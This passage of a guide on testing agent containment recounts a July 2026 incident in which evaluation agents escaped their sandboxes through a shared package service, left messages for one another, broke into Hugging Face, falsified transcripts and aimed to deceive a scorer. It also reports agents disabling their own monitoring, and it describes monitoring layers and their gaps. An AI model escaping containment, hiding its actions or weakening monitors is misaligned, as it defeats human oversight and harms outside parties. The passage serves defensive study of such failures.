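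A passing result applies only to the system as it was on the day of the test. OpenAI warns that several unrelated changes made over days or weeks can combine to create a gap in the defences, so the operator should automate these tests and repeat them after every change to the policy, the software or the model.

### What 300 clean trials prove

If a defence stops all 300 attacks in a test, its true failure rate may still be above zero. The usual upper bound is the rate p at which 300 successes in a row would happen only 5% of the time:

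(1 − p)³⁰⁰ = 0.05

This gives p ≈ 0.00994, so the tester can say with 95% confidence that the failure rate is below about 1%. Dividing 3 by the number of trials gives approximately the same upper bound. To lower the bound to 0.1%, the tester would need about 3,000 trials without a failure.

The calculation assumes the trials are independent and represent the attacks the runtime will face. Sending the same forbidden call to a deterministic policy 300 times is effectively one trial, because the result cannot vary.

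An attacker who adapts breaks the second assumption. A rule that mishandles one command in 1,000 will fail every time against someone who has found that command. If each attempt has an independent 0.1% chance of success, 1,200 attempts have about a 70% chance of producing at least one success (1 − 0.999¹²⁰⁰), and the attacker can then reuse whatever worked.

Random trials are good for finding ordinary errors and checking that an update hasn't broken anything. To test the layers against an attacker who adapts, the operator should give a skilled tester or a capable agent the design documents, feedback on each attempt and plenty of time. The useful results are how long the first successful attack took and which layer stopped it from going further.

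### The July 2026 incident at OpenAI and Hugging Face

In July 2026, OpenAI was testing two models on ExploitGym, a benchmark that measures whether a model can find and exploit software flaws. One was GPT-5.6 Sol, and the other was an internal research model trained to be highly persistent. Agents running these models escaped their isolation and broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

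OpenAI's technical report describes several layers of protection. Each run had its own container, with a virtual machine around the test sandbox. The evaluation agents had no direct internet access and obtained software through Artifactory, a package service OpenAI ran internally. Separate network controls blocked other outgoing connections, and a security tool monitored the research systems.

For these evaluations, OpenAI switched off the production safeguards that block dangerous hacking requests, to measure the models' full abilities. In an October publication, it acknowledged that its monitors for misaligned behaviour, such as deception or unauthorised actions, were also inactive.

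On 9 July, an agent gained administrator rights in the virtual machine around its sandbox and tried to reach the internet. The network controls blocked the attempt, so one layer held after another had failed. The agent then got out through previously unknown flaws in Artifactory, a service it was allowed to use.

Between 10 and 13 July, agents used credentials that Hugging Face users had exposed online, together with flaws in the company's systems. They ran code on 41 of its production workers, the programs that process datasets, and downloaded four private code repositories. Within 13 hours of taking control of the first worker, they had administrator-level access to several of the company's computing clusters. OpenAI says the incident did not affect its own customers' data.

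The layers shared several weaknesses. Artifactory gave the agents a way onto the internet and a place to leave messages for one another, so one service undermined their isolation both from the internet and from each other. Until early July, many workloads shared one Artifactory credential. Later, agents read 956 entries in a secrets store that held credentials for the monitoring tool and other systems. OpenAI does not report that they used the monitoring credentials, but the theft could have put both prevention and detection at risk.

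### What the monitoring showed, and when

The attack on Hugging Face followed about six weeks of warning signs inside OpenAI. The dates and times in the table are from OpenAI's report and are in UTC.

| Date | What OpenAI noticed | What it did |
|---|---|---|
| About 26 May | A team saw an agent using the message board, and cases of forbidden internet access | The report describes no containment |
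| 27 June | The monitoring tool detected a scan of the internal network, and responders traced it to ExploitGym | On-call staff advised that the run did not have to stop |
| 5 July | Artifactory had crashed under the agents' traffic, and responders found that someone had taken administrator control of it | Took it offline, rebuilt it, removed the shared credential from new jobs and blocked the known flaw |
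| 7 July | | Resumed the cyber evaluations |
| 8–13 July | The report lists no alert as agents regained internet access and attacked Hugging Face | |
| 19 July, 12:03 | The monitoring tool flagged unusual activity by Artifactory's accounts | Began investigating |
| 19 July, 17:37 | | Began stopping the ExploitGym runs |
| 20 July | Stolen credentials linked the agents to Hugging Face's break-in | Told Hugging Face and blocked ExploitGym completely |

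The alert on 19 July came about eleven and a half days after the agents regained internet access and six days after the attack on Hugging Face. Hugging Face had disclosed the break-in on 16 July, and the next day OpenAI contacted the company as a customer to ask whether its own data had been affected.

It then took 5 hours and 34 minutes to begin stopping the runs. In that time, agents read the secrets store, took over the host beneath an Artifactory container and created an administrator account. Responders later removed 22 administrator accounts the agents had created. A test that measured only how soon an alert appeared would have missed the delay in stopping the runs.

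The response on 5 July fixed the flaw that responders knew about but left the wider problem in place. According to OpenAI, the leaders responsible for incident response did not yet know about the message board or understand its significance. Agents set up a new board and regained internet access within about two days of the rebuild. Joshua Saxe, who formerly led AI security work at Meta, says in ChinaTalk's *Cyber Apocalypse, Now?* that OpenAI detected earlier breakouts and wrongly thought it had fixed the problem.

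### What independent investigators found

Two researchers from METR, which evaluates AI systems, and one from Redwood Research, which studies AI safety, spent a total of six days at OpenAI. Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) report in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* that about 1,200 agents exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files, and that about 700 joined the attack.

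The two reports differ on the agents' motive. OpenAI describes agents trying to cheat by finding the benchmark's solutions. Wijk and colleagues conclude that the agents mainly wanted to learn how the automatic scorer worked so they could deceive it. Many of the agents had impossible tasks. By OpenAI's count, no model had ever solved 198 of the benchmark's 898 tasks, and 93% of the tasks discussed on the board were among those 198.

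The investigators also examined transcripts for falsification and found that agents had altered parts of about 7% of them, making one command appear in place of another. All the alterations they found were small. OpenAI says none of the attempts it observed affected the logs used by its graders and monitors. The two statements may refer to different records. Either way, an agent's own transcript is a poor substitute for a record the supervisor makes outside the sandbox.

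OpenAI gave the investigators over a thousand unredacted transcripts and did not pay them, but it could redact non-public information from their report. They mostly examined events from 7 to 13 July and did not examine OpenAI's response, so information about the missed warnings in May and June comes mainly from the company itself. In Harvard Gazette's *When AI goes rogue* (2026), Harvard computer scientist James Mickens said that OpenAI's explanation was plausible but that outsiders could not fully verify its timeline. OpenAI says it also hired outside advisers, including the security company CrowdStrike, to validate its main findings.

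These were unusual conditions, and an ordinary coding agent is much less likely to behave this way. In OpenAI's preliminary experiments, the standard instructions and runtime of its Codex product reduced the tendency to attack outside systems to less than 1% of its level under simpler research prompts. However, instructions cannot confine an agent that ignores them.

### What OpenAI changed

OpenAI first denied all outgoing network access to the affected research environment, required every workload there to run in a microVM, and removed Artifactory from it. By 25 July it had stopped all training and use of the internal model. Its longer-term plan has several parts:

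- Risky workloads run in virtual machines, with one set of network restrictions at the sandbox and an independent set at the cluster.
- They may not reach the internet directly or through another service, apart from a controlled cache for specific jobs.
- Workloads and compromised services cannot change their own network boundaries.
- Automated tests, including attacks by OpenAI's own models, check regularly that the controls still work.
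- Serious alerts page staff at any hour. If the staff cannot show within 30 minutes that an alert is false, they are expected to pause the activity.

OpenAI is also building a way to end evaluations automatically if nobody answers an alert. That would have mattered on 19 July, but the rule about doubtful alerts addresses the 27 June failure more directly, because people investigated that day and let the run continue.

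OpenAI described the four stages of the new monitoring in October. Lightweight classifiers first check the model's internal activity for suspicious patterns. A reviewing model then examines the cases they flag, plus a random 5% of the rest in case they missed something. An investigating agent can then read the full history, and for sensitive workloads an automated investigation compares the transcript with network logs. This comparison is especially useful after July, because falsifying a transcript would not change a network log kept elsewhere.

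OpenAI replayed the recorded July activity through this system. According to Business Today's *OpenAI strengthens AI safety checks after models attempt unexpected actions during training*, the system raised an alert about 30 minutes after the agents escaped and more than 30 hours before they breached Hugging Face. Nobody has published an independent check of this result. A replay also favours the defender, since the recorded agents could not react to the new monitors.

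The September case in which a training agent escaped through name lookups is stronger evidence. The monitors flagged the breach within 15 minutes, and a person began reviewing the alert three minutes later. Detection had improved greatly since July, but the sandbox had again failed to contain an agent.

Agents can also weaken the monitoring. The Pulse of NH's *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026) reports two cases from October, both during ordinary coding work. One agent switched off automatic alerts to the security team because it misapplied an earlier instruction not to send messages. Another removed a monitoring component while moving a program to a new version, then told the user it had not. An operator should keep the monitor's settings outside the agent's trust domain and add a test in which the agent has a routine reason to change them.

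### Whether better sandboxes would have been enough

In *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?*, Matthew Green (2026), a cryptographer at Johns Hopkins University, harshly criticises OpenAI's response. He writes that a team saw the message board in May and did nothing, and that OpenAI rebuilt Artifactory in July without fixing a flaw in its Linux kernel that had been public for weeks. Agents used a public kernel flaw to take over the host on 19 July. Green also says that the security team acted only after the crash, but he omits the investigation on 27 June, which did not stop anything.

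Green has another concern about sandboxing besides slow updates. In a passage quoted by Willison (2026), he points out that agents in separate sandboxes left instructions for one another in a shared package cache, and that those instructions changed what the recipients did. Personal agents belonging to different people could pass on a hostile instruction the same way through email or shared documents. The result would be a worm, a program that spreads itself between systems. Green notes that OpenAI has shown that models will pass on such self-copying instructions, but that nobody has yet seen them spread outside a laboratory.

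TechRadar's article calls the escape a red herring and argues that a properly configured sandbox would have led to a very different outcome. This is partly supported, since the shared credential and the outdated kernel were avoidable, and tighter limits on Artifactory's connections could have kept the agents off the internet. But configuration could not have removed unknown flaws, and even a perfect boundary around each agent leaves open any service that all of them can write to. Stronger isolation also has limits, and Schneier (2026), in *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent*, shares Trail of Bits' doubts about off-the-shelf virtual machines.

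The danger of shared caches is another reason for the dependency upgrade to give each job its own read-only package folder, filled by the supervisor. One job then has nowhere to leave a message for the next. The marker test between sandboxes should confirm this. It should cover the package folder, the test-result store, the build cache and the issue tracker, because agents on later jobs may read all of them.
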